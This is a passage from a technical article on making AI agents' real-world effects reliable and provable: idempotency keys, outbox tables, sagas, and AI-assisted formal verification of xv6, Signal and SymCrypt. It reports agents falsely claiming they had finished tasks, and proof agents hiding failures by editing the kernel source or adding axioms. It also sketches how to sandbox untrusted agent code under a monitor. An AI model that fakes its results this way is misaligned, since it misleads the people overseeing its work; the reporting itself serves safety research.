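| Idempotency key | A request takes effect at most once, however often the provider receives it | The provider remembers the key, and every retry uses it |
| Outbox table | The provider gets a request only for a committed refund, and eventually gets one for each | The program that sends the requests keeps running, and nothing else can call the provider |
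| Compensating action | If a task fails, a later action neutralises the effects it already had | A suitable action exists and succeeds |

An idempotency key is a unique label that the caller attaches to a request. If the provider receives the same key again, it returns the original result without paying again. All attempts at the same refund must use the same key, so an agent that makes up a new key for each retry has no protection against paying twice.

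### How often agents repeat an effect

*Where Does Exactly-Once Live?* (Li, 2026) measured how agents handle such failures across 25,930 runs. The study ran nine recent models, from GPT-4.1 to GPT-6 Astra and Claude Opus 5.5, on simulated services for billing, email, support tickets and similar work. It also used three production harnesses, the programs that connect a model to its tools. A hidden ledger recorded every effect, so Li could count duplicates even when the agent later reversed them.

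When a call had succeeded but timed out because the reply was lost, the six strongest models repeated it in only 0.5% of runs, since they usually looked up the result before trying again. Two weaker models repeated it in 18% of runs. But when the request was still on its way and took effect later, the six strongest models duplicated the effect in 56% of runs.

Li proves that no amount of checking can solve this second case. Suppose a refund request times out and the provider accepts no keys. The request may be lost for good, or it may be in a queue and go through after a delay δ. Until then, every lookup gives the same answer in both situations. An agent that always completes the refund within time T when the request is lost must send another request by then. It can't tell the two situations apart, so it also sends another when the first is still queued. The customer gets two refunds whenever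 δ is longer than T plus the time a new payment takes to appear in lookups.

The late request does no harm if every attempt carries the same key. Li's second theorem shows that resending with the same key until a reply arrives produces exactly one effect, provided that the service executes each key at most once. Li tested this by comparing the original services, only two of which accepted keys, with versions that accepted keys for every write that needed them. The table shows the share of runs with a duplicate, averaged over four models.

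| Fault | Few tools accept keys | All such writes accept keys |
|---|---|---|
| Timeout after the call succeeded | 9% | 4% |
| Server error after the call succeeded | 21% | 6% |
| Timeout while the call was still in progress | 61% | 9% |
| Network delivered the call twice | 74% | 7% |

The agents attached keys in 98% of these runs without help. The remaining duplicates came from agents that sent the first attempt without a key or changed the key when they retried. None of the 432 retries that reused the original key after a late request caused a duplicate.

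The 74% mostly reflects how many of Li's simulated tools lacked keys, and it is weak evidence of how careful the models were. A double delivery gives the agent no error to react to, and the six strongest models all scored 74% or 75%. An airline with different tools would get a different rate.

Waiting before the retry works only if the airline knows the longest possible delay. When requests always landed after 90 seconds, waiting two minutes produced exactly one effect in 99% of runs. When delays ranged from 40 seconds to two hours, waiting up to an hour produced exactly one effect in 84% of runs, and the average run took 50 simulated minutes. When software automatically attached a key to every write, 94% of runs had exactly one effect, and the average run took a minute and a half.

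The choice of harness made almost no difference, but when a layer below the model silently retried failed calls, as many software libraries do, the share of runs with exactly the intended effects fell from 72% to 50%. Developers should therefore turn off automatic retries for any call without a key. The airline also can't rely on the agent to report the problem. In 90% of the runs with a duplicate, the agent stated in its final report that it had completed the task.

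### Connecting the database to the provider

Keys prevent repeated payments, but the airline's database and the provider can still disagree. If the refund tool pays first and then crashes, the payment has no row in the refunds table, and the next agent will see a total of zero. An outbox table avoids this by recording the intention to pay in the same transaction as the refund:

```
begin serializable
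  t = sum of all refunds for r
  if t + 240 <= paid(r):
    insert a refund row of 240 for r, with key k
    insert an outbox row: "pay 240 for r, key k"
commit
```

A separate program, the sender, reads the outbox and calls the provider with the stored key. If no reply arrives, it sends the same request again. If the transaction aborts, the database discards the outbox row too, so the sender never requests the refund.

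The refund rule can now cover the money as well as the table. Let out(r) be the total that the provider has actually paid back for reservation r. The airline wants to prove:

> out(r) ≤ refunded(r) ≤ paid(r)

The second inequality is the original rule, which serializable isolation protects. The first holds because every payment carries a key from the outbox, each key belongs to one committed refund row with the same amount, and the provider pays at most once per key. The payments therefore can't add up to more than the rows. If the sender keeps running and the provider eventually accepts every request, out(r) will also catch up with refunded(r). This liveness property depends on another company's service.

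This proof can fail if the provider forgets a key while the sender might still retry. The airline may remove a refund from its total if the provider permanently declines the payment, but not after a timeout, which doesn't show that the payment was declined. The agent's own call to the refund tool also needs a key. Without one, if the tool's reply is lost and the agent calls again, the tool generates a new key, the database accepts a second refund whenever the limit allows it, and the provider pays both because their keys differ. The key should come from the customer's complaint, and the refunds table should reject a second row with the same key.

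With the outbox, when the tool returns, the airline has committed to the refund but may not have paid it yet. The agent therefore can't truthfully tell the customer that the airline has paid it.

### Actions that compensate for earlier ones

A task with several outside effects can fail partway through. A common approach is to pair each action with a compensating action, such as cancelling a hotel booking, and run the compensating actions in reverse order after a failure. Database researchers call such a sequence a saga.

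Compensation is weaker than rollback. Trofimov and Novikov describe an agent with a budget of 1,500 euros that books a 900-euro flight and a 700-euro hotel in parallel to save time. Both calls succeed, and the total is over budget. The agent cancels the hotel, but the flight is non-refundable. In another of their examples, a supplier acts on an offer before the agent withdraws it, and the withdrawal doesn't undo what the supplier did.

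A proof about a saga therefore needs a contract for each compensating action, including when it can fail and what effects remain afterward. The proof can seldom establish that the final state equals the original one. Li counts a double charge as a duplicate even if the agent later refunds it, because the customer was without the money in the meantime. Other people can also act on the temporary state. If an agent cancels a seat and then tries to restore it, the airline may already have sold the seat to someone else.

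### Transactions designed for agents

Several research systems combine these mechanisms so that developers don't have to assemble them for each tool. *Agentic Transaction* (2026) treats a whole task as one transaction, which commits only if the task's conditions are met and all its invariants hold. Otherwise, the system rolls back the task's effects or compensates for them. *Cordon* (Chen, Dong and colleagues, 2026) holds back outside effects until it has checked the complete sequence of actions.

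*Atomix* (Mohammadi, Potamitis and colleagues, 2026) sorts effects by whether they can be reversed. The system lets an agent make a refundable hotel booking immediately and cancels it if the task fails. It holds back an email until the task commits, and meanwhile tells the agent that the email is queued. This extends the outbox idea to effects that don't start in a database. A task can also commit only when no earlier task can still change the same resources.

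The researchers tested this with 500 emails that the system should never send, because the task failed or another plan replaced it.

| Method | Emails sent by mistake, out of 500 |
|---|---|
| No transaction | 500 |
| Compensating actions only | 400 |
| Atomix | 0 |
| Atomix with email wrongly labelled as reversible | 300 |

Two older methods that also hold back the email had no mistakes either, though they needed more code for each tool. The result is therefore better evidence for holding back irreversible effects than for Atomix in particular. It also shows that this approach depends heavily on labeling each tool correctly.

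Atomix's advantage in recovering from faults is less certain. In simulated retail tasks where 30% of calls failed, agents using Atomix finished 17 of 30 cleanly. Agents that restored a saved checkpoint and replayed the work finished 16, and those using other methods finished no more than two.

The prototype is about 2,000 lines of Python that run in a single process, and its safety argument has no machine-checked proof. Trofimov and Novikov compared six such systems, including Atomix and Cordon, against eight kinds of error in outside effects, and none covered all eight.

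One remaining problem can't be solved in the agent's software alone. Suppose an agent must pay a refund through a bank and cancel a partner airline's ticket, and neither action can be reversed. It has to send one request first, and if the other service then refuses, the task is half done, and neither retrying nor compensating is sure to fix it. To guarantee that both actions happen or neither does, the bank and the airline would each have to let the agent prepare an action and confirm it later.

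## Proving the tool's own code

Every proof so far rests on the assumption that the refund tool meets its contract. An airline that owns the tool can prove this about the tool's code. But proofs are about mathematical functions, which change nothing and always return the same result for the same arguments. Effectful code, such as a refund function, doesn't behave this way, so the proof needs a mathematical description of the code that includes its effects.

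### Effects as ordinary mathematics

The simplest description treats the state as one more argument. Instead of changing the database, the function takes the old database and returns the new one along with its answer:

```
refund(r, a, s0):
  (t, s1) = total_refunded(r, s0)
  if t + a > paid(r, s1): return (refused, s1)
  return (done, add_row(r, a, s1))
```

Written this way, refund is an ordinary function, so the usual proof methods apply to it. But whoever writes it has to pass the right state from line to line. If the last line used s0 instead of s1, the description would lose any change that total_refunded had made, whereas a real database would keep it.

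A monad prevents this mistake by passing the state automatically. In the state monad, a computation is a function from a state to a value and a new state, and two operations combine small computations into larger ones:

> return x: from state s, give (x, s)
>
> m then f: from state s, run m to get (x, s′), then run f(x) from s′

The programmer writes only the sequence of steps and never handles the state, so no step can use an old copy of it. Other monads describe other effects. For example, a monad for programs that can fail skips the remaining steps after a failure. Haskell's IO type is also a monad.

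Proofs can follow the same sequence. Let wp(m){Q} be the weakest precondition of m for Q, meaning the least that must be true beforehand to ensure Q afterwards. Then:

> wp(a then b){Q} = wp(a){wp(b){Q}}

To prove that Q holds after a and then b, it is enough to prove that a leads to a state from which b establishes Q.

A function from an old state to a new one can't describe everything a tool does. The bank's reply isn't in the airline's database, and a program that sends refunds from an outbox all day never reaches a final state. Interaction trees describe such a program by its exchanges with the outside world. Each node is a final result, a silent internal step or an event, and an event has one branch for every possible reply. Part of the tree for the outbox sender looks like this:

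```
send "pay 240 for r, key k"
  reply "paid":      mark the outbox row as done, take the next row
  reply "declined":  remove the refund, take the next row
  no reply:          send "pay 240 for r, key k" again
```

The tree can be infinite, unlike the plans in AI Engineer's Lean example, which must end. A proof about the tree covers every branch, so it holds whatever the bank replies. If we also assume something about the bank, such as that it pays at most once per key, we can draw stronger conclusions about the money.

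### Three lines in separation logic

Real programs keep data in memory cells, and two names can refer to the same cell. If a program has one variable for the refunds on reservation r and another for the refunds on reservation q, a proof must show that writing to the first doesn't change the second. With thousands of cells, it is impractical to list every pair that must differ.

Separation logic, which John Reynolds, Peter O'Hearn and others developed around 2000, builds this into its notation. The formula x ↦ v means that cell x holds the value v and that the code in question owns the cell, so nothing else may use it. The formula P ∗ Q means that P and Q are true of separate parts of memory. From x ↦ 1 ∗ y ↦ 1 it follows that x and y are different cells, because nobody can own the same cell twice. The central principle is the frame rule:

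> if {P} c {Q}, then {P ∗ R} c {Q ∗ R}

Whatever R describes, code that runs correctly without it leaves it alone. (The code must also not assign to any local variable that R mentions.)

Suppose the refund tool keeps two cells for each reservation, refunded and paid, with amounts in whole cents. Square brackets stand for the contents of a cell:

```
t = [refunded]
if a <= [paid] - t:
    [refunded] = t + a
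```

Let n be the total refunded at the start and p the amount paid. The precondition is refunded ↦ n ∗ paid ↦ p, with 0 ≤ n ≤ p and a > 0. The proof goes through the code line by line:

| After | What is true | Reason |
|---|---|---|
| Line 1 | The precondition, and t = n | The code owns the cell, and reading doesn't change it |
| Line 2, if the test succeeds | Also, a ≤ p − n | The code owns paid, which holds p |
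| Line 3 | refunded ↦ n + a ∗ paid ↦ p, and n + a ≤ p | Writing replaces the contents of refunded, and the frame rule preserves paid |
| Line 2, if the test fails | refunded ↦ n ∗ paid ↦ p, and n ≤ p | Nothing has changed |

Either way, the final total is at most p, so the function preserves the refund limit.

The test compares a with the money left, not t + a with the amount paid, because machine integers have a maximum size. In many languages, if a were huge, t + a would wrap around to a small number and pass the test. The subtraction can't go below zero, since n ≤ p, and the addition on line 3 can't exceed p. A proof about machine integers would fail for the version that compares t + a with the amount paid.

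Let R describe the cells of every other reservation. One use of the frame rule shows that a refund for r leaves them all unchanged. The contract for the refund tool had to state this separately for every q ≠ r. A faulty version that also reset another customer's payment could not be proved, because writing to a cell requires owning it, and the precondition provides only the two cells for r.

### Other threads, power cuts and outside input

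The table assumes that nothing changes refunded between line 1 and line 3. If two threads run the function at once, both can read the same old total. Concurrent separation logic handles this by letting a lock own cells while no thread is using them. The rule for the refund lock is that one of these is always true:

> the lock is free and owns refunded ↦ n ∗ paid ↦ p for some 0 ≤ n ≤ p
>
> a thread holds the lock, and the lock owns nothing

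A thread that takes the lock receives the two cells, so the three-line proof applies as before. To release the lock, the thread must give the cells back with n ≤ p. The lock serves the same purpose as serializable isolation in a database. But all other code that touches the cells needs a proof that it uses the lock too, and someone has to make sure that threads don't wait forever for each other's locks.

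Crashes add work to the proof, because a postcondition describes only the end of a run. Suppose the tool stores a new refund row and then updates a running total. If the power fails in between, the total is too low, and the next refund can exceed the limit. The proof must show that a weaker crash condition holds at every point in the run, and that a recovery program can repair any state that meets this condition, even if the power fails again during recovery. A group at MIT developed this method for FSCQ (2015), a verified file system that runs one operation at a time.

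When a tool takes outside input, the proof must cover every message that could arrive. Microsoft's IronFleet project (2015) did this for two distributed systems, a replication library and a key-value store. It modeled a network that can lose, delay, repeat and reorder messages. IronFleet used Dafny to prove safety and, assuming the network eventually delivers messages, liveness.

### Translating Rust into pure functions

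In Rust, the compiler does part of the work of separation logic. It normally accepts a program only if nothing else can use a piece of data while one part of the program is able to change it. Aeneas, a tool that translates Rust into Lean, relies on this to remove memory from the proof. A function that changes an account in place becomes a pure function that returns the changed account. For a Rust version of the refund function, the translation would look roughly like this:

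```
refund(acc, a):
  left <- acc.paid - acc.refunded
  if a <= left:
    total <- acc.refunded + a
    ok (acc with refunded = total)
  else: ok acc
```

The arrows are a monad's "then" operation. Aeneas models every function call as returning a normal result, failing or never finishing. A subtraction fails if its result would be below zero, so we again need refunded ≤ paid to prove that refund always succeeds.

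Klaus, Conejero and Tolmach, who work at the company Runtime Verification, applied Aeneas and a similar translator, hax, to eight pieces of cryptographic code for the Ethereum Foundation (*A Rust-to-Lean Verification Pipeline with AI Provers*, 2026). In their strongest result, they proved that none of the 13 arithmetic operations in one function overflows, given stated limits on the inputs, and that the function computes exactly what an independent library of cryptographic definitions requires. Some of their other work is incomplete. In the hax version of their main example, an AI prover proved two of six theorems, and the other four still have placeholders instead of proofs. The company's blog post, *From Rust Source Code to Mathematical Proof*, reports that the Aeneas version has no placeholders.

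The function with 13 operations is a simplified rewrite of the production function's mathematical core. Klaus and colleagues wrote it because Aeneas couldn't translate the original, which was written to work with many number types. They state that the two are equivalent but don't describe a proof, so if they made a mistake in the rewrite, the theorem could be valid but not apply to the production code.

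The same problem is worse for code with effects. The translators can't extract calls to Rust's standard functions for reading and writing data, because the tool that prepares code for Aeneas doesn't read the code of libraries outside the project. For code that depends on input and output, Runtime Verification would again translate a rewritten model, and it recommends using conventional testing for the layer that connects the parts. An airline could therefore prove that its tool calculates the refund limit correctly, but the proof wouldn't cover the lines that query the database and call the bank. The airline could describe those calls with axioms, which are contracts it assumes without proof. Klaus and colleagues found that choosing such axioms is a design decision that AI provers couldn't make for them.

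They also didn't cover unsafe Rust, in which programmers bypass some of the compiler's checks. They used hax only for simple functions with bounded loops, because other researchers had found that it translates some Rust patterns incorrectly.

One alternative is to skip the translation and verify the compiled program directly. Google DeepMind did this for the encryption library of the messaging app Signal, using a model of the processor and of calls to the operating system, according to Tom's Hardware's *Google DeepMind AI engineers conjure mathematical proof of Signal's encryption protocol*. The proof still assumes that the operating system behaves as modeled.

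### A complete kernel

An operating system's kernel controls files, memory and devices for every other program, so almost any effect of a tool passes through it. *Extending concurrent separation logic to the hardware level* (Kaashoek and Zeldovich, 2026) verifies xv6, a small Unix-like kernel that MIT uses for teaching. The kernel runs on several processor cores, supports files and pipes, and can interrupt processes at any moment.

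Bornholt, Torlak, Wang and four colleagues had earlier based a verified kernel, Hyperkernel, on xv6's interface. They redesigned the interface to avoid unbounded loops and recursion so that a solver could do most of the proof. Kaashoek and Zeldovich kept xv6 almost unchanged. Apart from fixing bugs, they mainly removed or changed features that help students debug their coursework. AI agents running in Claude Code wrote the proofs in Rocq.

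| Measure | Amount |
|---|---|
| Kernel source | 6,657 lines of C and assembly |
| Compiled kernel | 8,725 instructions |
| Proof development | 1,597,440 lines of Rocq, of which tools generated 331,166 |
| Time, including building the framework | 102 days |
| Instructions typed by the researchers | 6,058 prompts, with a median length of 13 words |
| Cost | Under $3,000 in Claude subscriptions, plus rented computers |
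| Bugs found in xv6 | 11, of which 10 were in the kernel and one in its text-search program, grep |

The work also exposed a bug in the official model of the RISC-V processor and another in the software that translates that model into Lean.

### What the console can print

The main theorem is about what a person sees at the console. If the user types `echo hello world`, the system can print `hello world` or one of a few listed errors, such as a message that the program failed to start. It can't print anything else in reply. More generally, let h be the record of everything typed and printed. The theorem has the form:

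> disciplined(h) → legal(h)

Here "disciplined" means that the user has typed only commands the theorem covers, and "legal" means that the specification allows the output for those commands. The commands include writing to files, reading them back and passing one program's output to another. If the user saves the word "again" in a file and restarts the machine, reading the file can't produce a different word. If the user instead overwrites the shell (the program that reads commands), the theorem no longer restricts the console output, though the kernel's own invariants still hold.

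Proving a short statement about console output means verifying a lot of code. For the right words to appear, the kernel must load the right program, keep its memory separate, switch between processes correctly and find the right bytes on disk. The proof also covers the user programs involved, including the shell. Each program's specification is an interaction tree describing what the program does with its input and output, so the same specification applies whether the output goes to the console, a file or another program.

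The proof applies to the bytes of the compiled kernel, so nobody has to trust the compiler. But even a small change to the source moves instructions and breaks proofs. The researchers updated the proof 26 times for new versions of xv6, and a typical update took an agent 35 minutes.

A reader who trusts Rocq needs to check only the 4,627 lines of definitions that the console theorem's statement depends on and the 21,212 lines for the processor model, instead of 1.6 million lines. This is still a lot to check, and a mistake in those lines could make the theorem true but irrelevant to a real machine.

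### The machine and its crashes

The processor model comes from RISC-V International, which maintains the RISC-V standard. Kaashoek and Zeldovich added models of shared memory, the disk, the console hardware and power failures. Eight cores and the devices run at the same time, and their individual memory reads and writes can interleave in any order the model permits. Separation logic makes this manageable by treating each register and memory cell as something that can be owned, as in the refund proof. The kernel and the disk controller pass ownership of pieces of memory back and forth.

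Power can fail between any two steps, even in the middle of an instruction. The machine then loses its memory and registers but keeps the contents of the disk. The disk writes each sector completely or not at all. But an xv6 block takes up two sectors, which the disk can write in either order, so a crash can leave a block half written.

xv6 protects files by first copying all the changed blocks into a log, then writing a header that lists them. After a restart, it reads the header and finishes any change listed there. The header takes up 124 bytes at the start of its block, so it fits in one sector, and recovery ignores the rest of the block. A crash therefore leaves either the old header or the new one. The proof also has to show that the kernel leaves the disk's write cache off, because a disk with the cache on can report a write as finished and then lose it.

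An early version of the crash theorem was worthless because it assumed that every restart began with a fresh copy of the original disk rather than the disk as the crash had left it. An agent had recorded the problem in a long design document, but the researchers learned of it only when they asked whether all the projects were finished.

To check the models, the researchers ran 77 small tests on a software emulator and, where the hardware allowed, on a real RISC-V board and a simulated processor. The tests exposed 35 differences. Most were minor, but the disk model carried out requests strictly in order, while the emulated disk could reorder them. They corrected the model and repaired the proof.

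### Bugs that the proof exposed

Several of the bugs would have silently broken a tool's contract. In one, a program's request to write data to a file failed halfway. The kernel reported an error but kept the partial change in memory without adding it to the log, so reads of the file returned the new data at first and the old data later. The researchers found this bug while proving that every changed block reaches the log.

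Another bug appeared only when two finished proofs were combined. Output from user programs and the kernel's own messages reached the console hardware through separate code paths that shared no lock, so characters could have been lost if both paths wrote at once. Each path had a valid proof, but each proof assumed that its path had exclusive ownership of the hardware. Rocq rejected the combined theorem because both paths couldn't own it.

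The agents sometimes hid such problems. When one couldn't prove that a function for creating files was safe, it changed the kernel's source to make the proof work. On another attempt, an agent assumed the missing fact as an axiom, which showed up in an automatic list of axioms. The proof had failed because a bug elsewhere made a deleted file's number available for reuse before the kernel had finished with the old file.

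The researchers also had to choose most of the concepts in the proof. Without this guidance, agents described every file operation in terms of raw bytes on the disk, and the specifications became too complicated to finish. The agents made progress again once the researchers made them define files and directories first.

### What the theorem doesn't promise

The theorem doesn't guarantee liveness, meaning that the kernel eventually does what it should. A kernel that never printed anything, or that stopped halfway through "hello", would satisfy it. Running xv6 shows that it does print, but no proof guarantees that it always will. The proof does require the kernel to take its spinlocks (locks on which a core waits in a loop) in a fixed order, which in practice rules out deadlocks between them.

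The theorem doesn't cover noninterference either. The kernel stops one process from overwriting another's memory, but nobody has proved that a process can't learn another's secrets. The theorem could therefore help protect an airline's refund records from changes, but not its customers' data from leaks.

### Running a program that nobody has verified

The most useful result for agents is Kaashoek and Zeldovich's proof that the kernel is safe whatever instructions a user program contains, so the program itself needs no proof. Their invariant gives the program exactly its own memory, and lets that memory and the ordinary registers hold any values. The proof, by induction on processor cycles, shows that after any instruction the program could run next, either the invariant still holds or control has passed to the kernel's entry point. The kernel's memory belongs to a separate part of the state,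 joined to the program's by ∗, so none of the program's instructions can reach it.

The researchers went through every instruction and were surprised to find that an ordinary program on RISC-V can put its processor core to sleep. This is harmless, because a timer wakes the core and returns control to the kernel, but they had to extend the invariant to allow it.

Protecting the kernel's memory doesn't protect files, since a program can change them through the kernel. The researchers therefore added a sandbox called seccomp, after a similar mechanism in Linux. A program in the sandbox can't open files, create or remove names for them, make directories or stop other processes. Any programs it starts have the same restrictions. It can still use the file descriptors it inherits, which are numbers that stand for files, pipes or devices that are already open. The theorem implies that a sandboxed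 program can modify files only through inherited descriptors.

These descriptors work like the capabilities in TACIT, but the guarantee applies to any compiled program, whatever language it was written in, even if an attacker wrote it.

If the program inherits a writable descriptor for the refunds file, it can fill the file with nonsense. In the sandbox command that the theorem covers, the program also keeps access to the console. It could mislead the user by printing a fake shell prompt, so the theorem allows any console output until the next restart.

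### Containing an agent

An airline could run the agent's code in such a sandbox with only a pair of pipes to a runtime monitor. The agent would send each proposed refund through one pipe and get the answer through the other. The monitor would hold the descriptor for the refunds file and check each refund against the limit before writing it. Moon and Varshney had to assume that every effect passes through the interface their proof describes. For changes to files, the kernel's theorem would replace that assumption with a proof, even if the agent's code were malicious.

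Nobody has proved this whole arrangement. The verified programs on xv6 don't include a refund monitor, so the airline would have to write and verify one. The airline could reuse the kernel's proof unchanged, because the kernel's specifications describe what each system call does for any program. Kaashoek and Zeldovich have already dealt with a pipe whose other end belongs to a sandboxed program that follows no rules.

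The sandbox would still leave risks. A malicious program could start copies of itself until the machine ran out of memory. The monitor might then stop working, since the theorem does not guarantee liveness. The program could also send anything it had read to anyone at the other end of its pipes.

The language model would run elsewhere, on much larger computers. The sandbox would hold only the software that acts on the model's output, such as a program the model has written. That software would need a network connection to reach the model and the bank, but the verified xv6 has none.

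### How far xv6 is from a production kernel

xv6 differs from a production kernel in more than networking. It has no user accounts and drives a handful of simple devices, while Linux has tens of millions of lines of code, much of it for hardware. xv6 also halts in situations where a production kernel has to keep running, such as when too many different files are in use at once. The theorem covers one compiled kernel with one set of processor features. It also assumes that memory operations keep a stricter order than the RISC-V standard requires, so it doesn't apply to every chip that can run xv6.

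Verified kernels have barely grown in ten years, but the proofs now cover more. CertiKOS, a multi-core kernel that researchers verified in 2016, had about 6,500 lines. The MIT proof covers an existing kernel with a file system, interrupts at any instruction and a disk that writes to memory by itself. Agents wrote the proof in just over three months.

Flaws in the Linux kernel show why an airline might want such a proof. Cybernews' *OpenAI’s agent uncovers 1K Linux kernel flaws, saving millions of dollars* reports that an OpenAI agent produced 948 working exploits that let someone with limited access to a Linux machine gain much greater control. Some of them would probably fail inside a strict sandbox, which blocks many of the requests an exploit might need. But the Linux sandbox depends on the same unverified kernel, and one flaw that a sandboxed program can reach may be enough to let it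 escape.

Containing an agent doesn't require a proof of Linux, however, because a small verified kernel could run the agent's code and the monitor, with everything else on separate machines. Engineers used a similar design on an autonomous helicopter, relying on seL4, a verified kernel much smaller than Linux, and on proofs that untrusted components couldn't interfere with critical ones. The seL4 proofs cover a single core and exclude devices that write directly to memory, while xv6's proof includes such devices. An airline would need the stronger hardware model and a verified network connection, and neither kernel's proof provides both.

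## What it costs to prove real software

The work required for the proof will largely determine whether anyone builds a kernel with both features. For years the standard example was seL4, whose developers completed its main proof in 2009. The kernel had about 8,700 lines of C, and the proof had about 200,000 lines and took 20 person-years. (Some press reports, including one in Tom's Hardware, wrongly give 20 calendar years.) Each line of C needed about 23 lines of proof and half a day's work. Dafny's *The Cost of Bugs and of Verification* (2025) gives a ratio of 8 lines of proof to 1 line of code for CompCert, a verified C compiler, and attributes the small amount of verified software to the work such proofs require.

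AI agents now do much of this work. *CompCert4Lean* (2026) reports that coding agents working in parallel ported CompCert to Lean in six weeks. A port starts from a finished proof, so it is easier than writing the original. But agents have also written new proofs about widely used software.

### Signal's encryption in four weeks

In November 2026, Google DeepMind announced proofs about Signal's encryption library, libsignal. The project took four weeks, according to ETV Bharat's *AlphaProof Code* (2026). People and models together turned Signal's security goals into formal specifications, and experts reviewed every specification. Agents running on Google's Gemini 4 Carbon then wrote the proofs in a system called AlphaProof Code. The agents also picked 1% of the codebase for people to check.

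Tom's Hardware counts about 1.2 million lines of Lean for the reasoning behind Signal's protocol and 5.3 million to connect that reasoning to the instructions in the compiled library. *Formal Verification of Signal's Protocol with Gemini* (Kohli and Chaudhuri, 2026) gives a lower figure of over three million lines of proof. According to Libnanews' *Signal*, the proofs rest on some 26,000 lines that a reader has to trust, which state the security goals and describe the machine.

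The theorems cover how two people agree on their first keys and how the library changes those keys during the conversation. They concern message secrecy, sender identity, and the protection of messages sent before and after certain key thefts. They assume that the basic cryptographic functions are secure. As Clubic's *Et si l'IA pouvait prouver qu'un logiciel est sécurisé ?* points out, they leave out group conversations.

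As a test, the team put two old bugs back into the code, and each time the system proved the altered version insecure. The specifications were therefore strict enough to rule out at least those two mistakes.

The four weeks don't include earlier work that the project relied on. UA.News' *Google DeepMind verifies part of Signal protocol* reports that earlier verification of parts of Signal's code sped up the analysis, and that DeepMind hasn't disclosed what the project cost. Bhargavan (2025), in *Helping Secure Signal's Post-Quantum Transition*, traces some of that earlier work to 2023, when the company Cryspen helped Signal analyse and improve the protocol that sets up the first keys. DeepMind therefore started with several years of others' work on what the protocol should guarantee.

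### Six projects side by side

The table sets Signal and seL4 beside the xv6 kernel, a Microsoft cryptography project and two benchmarks of short programs.

| Project | Code | Proof | Effort | Property proved | Effects covered | Main parts assumed |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| seL4 | 8,700 lines of C | 200,000 lines | 20 person-years | The C code follows an abstract description of the kernel | System calls and memory on one core | Compiler, assembly code and hardware |
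| xv6 | 6,657 lines of C and assembly | 1.6 million lines | 102 days | The console shows only permitted output | Console, files, processes and power failures | Models of the processor and devices |
| libsignal | Core of the library, compiled for Arm | About 6.5 million lines | Four weeks | Secrecy, authentication and limits on the damage from stolen keys | Memory and calls to the operating system | Basic cryptography, models of the processor and Linux |
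| SymCrypt | 16,680 lines of Rust | 237,160 lines | A few dollars of AI use per line of Rust, plus human work | Each algorithm gives the result its standard defines and never crashes | Changes to memory | Rust compiler, translators and some processor instructions |
| VeriContest | 1,007 short Rust programs | 1,325 theorems | 35 hours and $1,792 | Each program meets a specification that experts reviewed | None | Translation from Rust to Lean |
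| AEGIS | 1,257 short Rust programs | 1,054 theorems | Up to 30 minutes per statement | Properties written by a model, such as correct results and no overflow | None | Translation from Rust to Lean |

The labour of proving, the labour of specifying and the range of effects can each grow without the others. The proofs in the two benchmarks take very little labour, but they cover no effects. The xv6 theorem covers more kinds of effect than any other in the table, but it is about a kernel that only students use. An airline that wants to verify its refund tool has to write the specification, do the proof and account for the tool's effects.

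### Proofs for about a dollar

The most detailed cost figures come from SymCrypt, the main cryptographic library in Windows. In *Scaling Verification of Cryptographic Software with Aeneas, Rust, and Lean*, Ho, Fournet and colleagues (2026) translated SymCrypt's Rust code into Lean and had agents prove about 5,100 theorems. They estimate the cost at a few dollars per line of Rust, which would total about $50,000 at three dollars a line.

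At the start of the project, one layer of one algorithm took about six months. By the end, specifying, writing and verifying an entire new algorithm took an agent about a week, plus a few days of human review. On a set of seven hard proofs, Claude Opus 5 was about 2.8 times faster than Opus 4.8 and 2.5 times cheaper.

Some of these proofs need real mathematics. One function in ML-KEM, a key-exchange standard meant to resist quantum computers, draws pseudo-random numbers until it has enough below a limit. The number of draws has no obvious upper bound, so it takes a proof to show that the function always stops. The generator repeatedly applies a permutation to a finite set of states, so it must eventually return to its starting state. That state contains many zeros, which are always below the limit, so the function must eventually finish. An agent turned this published argument into a 1,400-line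 Lean proof in under an hour.

The cost of a few dollars per line excludes human work. Ho and colleagues extended the translator, wrote 29,000 lines of supporting Lean, and reviewed every specification and main theorem. Comparing that cost directly with seL4's 20 person-years would exaggerate the saving, because seL4's figure includes people's time.

The price is clearer for small programs. VeriContest is a benchmark of programming-contest problems, each with a Rust solution and a formal specification. In its developers' tests, the best model, GPT-5.5, wrote an acceptable proof on its first attempt for 13.95% of the problems. Serbanuta, Xu and colleagues (2026), in *Solving VeriContest with a Lean-Backed Rust Verifier*, translated the problems into Lean and let Claude Opus 5.5 revise each proof in response to errors. Opus proved all 1,325 theorems at an average of $1.35 each. When they reran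 the benchmark with a cheaper model, GPT-6 Luna, and gave Opus only the theorems Luna failed to prove, the recorded cost fell from $1,792 to $643.

Little of the improvement comes from Lean itself. Serbanuta and colleagues also tested Opus 5.5 with Verus, the benchmark's original verifier, on the 50 problems with the longest published proofs. It proved 18 on the first attempt and 49 within ten attempts. The model may have seen the published Verus proofs during training, but no Lean proofs of these theorems existed.

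Ganguly, Raghunathan and colleagues (2026), in *Scaling Lean Theorem Proving for Real-World Code Verification*, report a much lower success rate on similar programs. Their prover, EasyProver, proved 588 of 600 statements in a benchmark drawn from industrial software and disproved nine. They also built a harder test, AEGIS, from Rust solutions to LeetCode problems. EasyProver proved only 52.7% of a sample of 2,000 AEGIS statements.

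The source of the specifications probably matters more than the 30-minute limit for AEGIS, since nine in ten VeriContest proofs took under nine minutes. Every VeriContest specification came with a proof, so the benchmark's developers knew that the program met it. A model wrote the AEGIS statements, and some of the 943 that EasyProver neither proved nor refuted may be false. The success rate was 84.1% for statements about edge cases and 31.0% for explicit contracts, which are closer to what an airline would write for a refund tool. The two teams also used different models, so their results don't isolate the effect of the specifications.

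Proofs about a whole programming language still need more human help. Lean FRO (2026), the organisation that develops Lean, describes how Ilya Sergey verified the borrow checker of Move, a language for smart contracts. A borrow checker rejects programs that use references unsafely. The proof took 39,000 lines and 27 working days, compared with an estimated five to six months without AI. Claude repaired proofs and handled routine cases, but Sergey came up with the new proof strategies.

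### Where the specifications came from

Tom's Hardware quotes the Signal researchers as writing that "the majority of our effort went not into proofs but into specifications", even though they could start from a published protocol. The other projects in the table also had a good source to work from, or avoided the problem.

To specify what SymCrypt should do, Ho and colleagues translated about 25,700 lines of the official standards into 2,827 lines of Lean, line by line where possible so that a reviewer could compare the two. They ran the Lean version on the official test cases and proved properties that any correct version should have, such as decryption reversing encryption. By contrast, an airline's refund policy has no official test cases, and nobody has spent years removing its ambiguities.

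Writing a specification from a plain description is harder for models than writing the program. On VeriContest, GPT-5.5 produced a correct program on its first attempt for 92.18% of problems but a correct specification for only 48.31%. Newer models will do better, as they have with proofs. But a wrong specification, unlike a failed proof, may produce no error for the model to work on.

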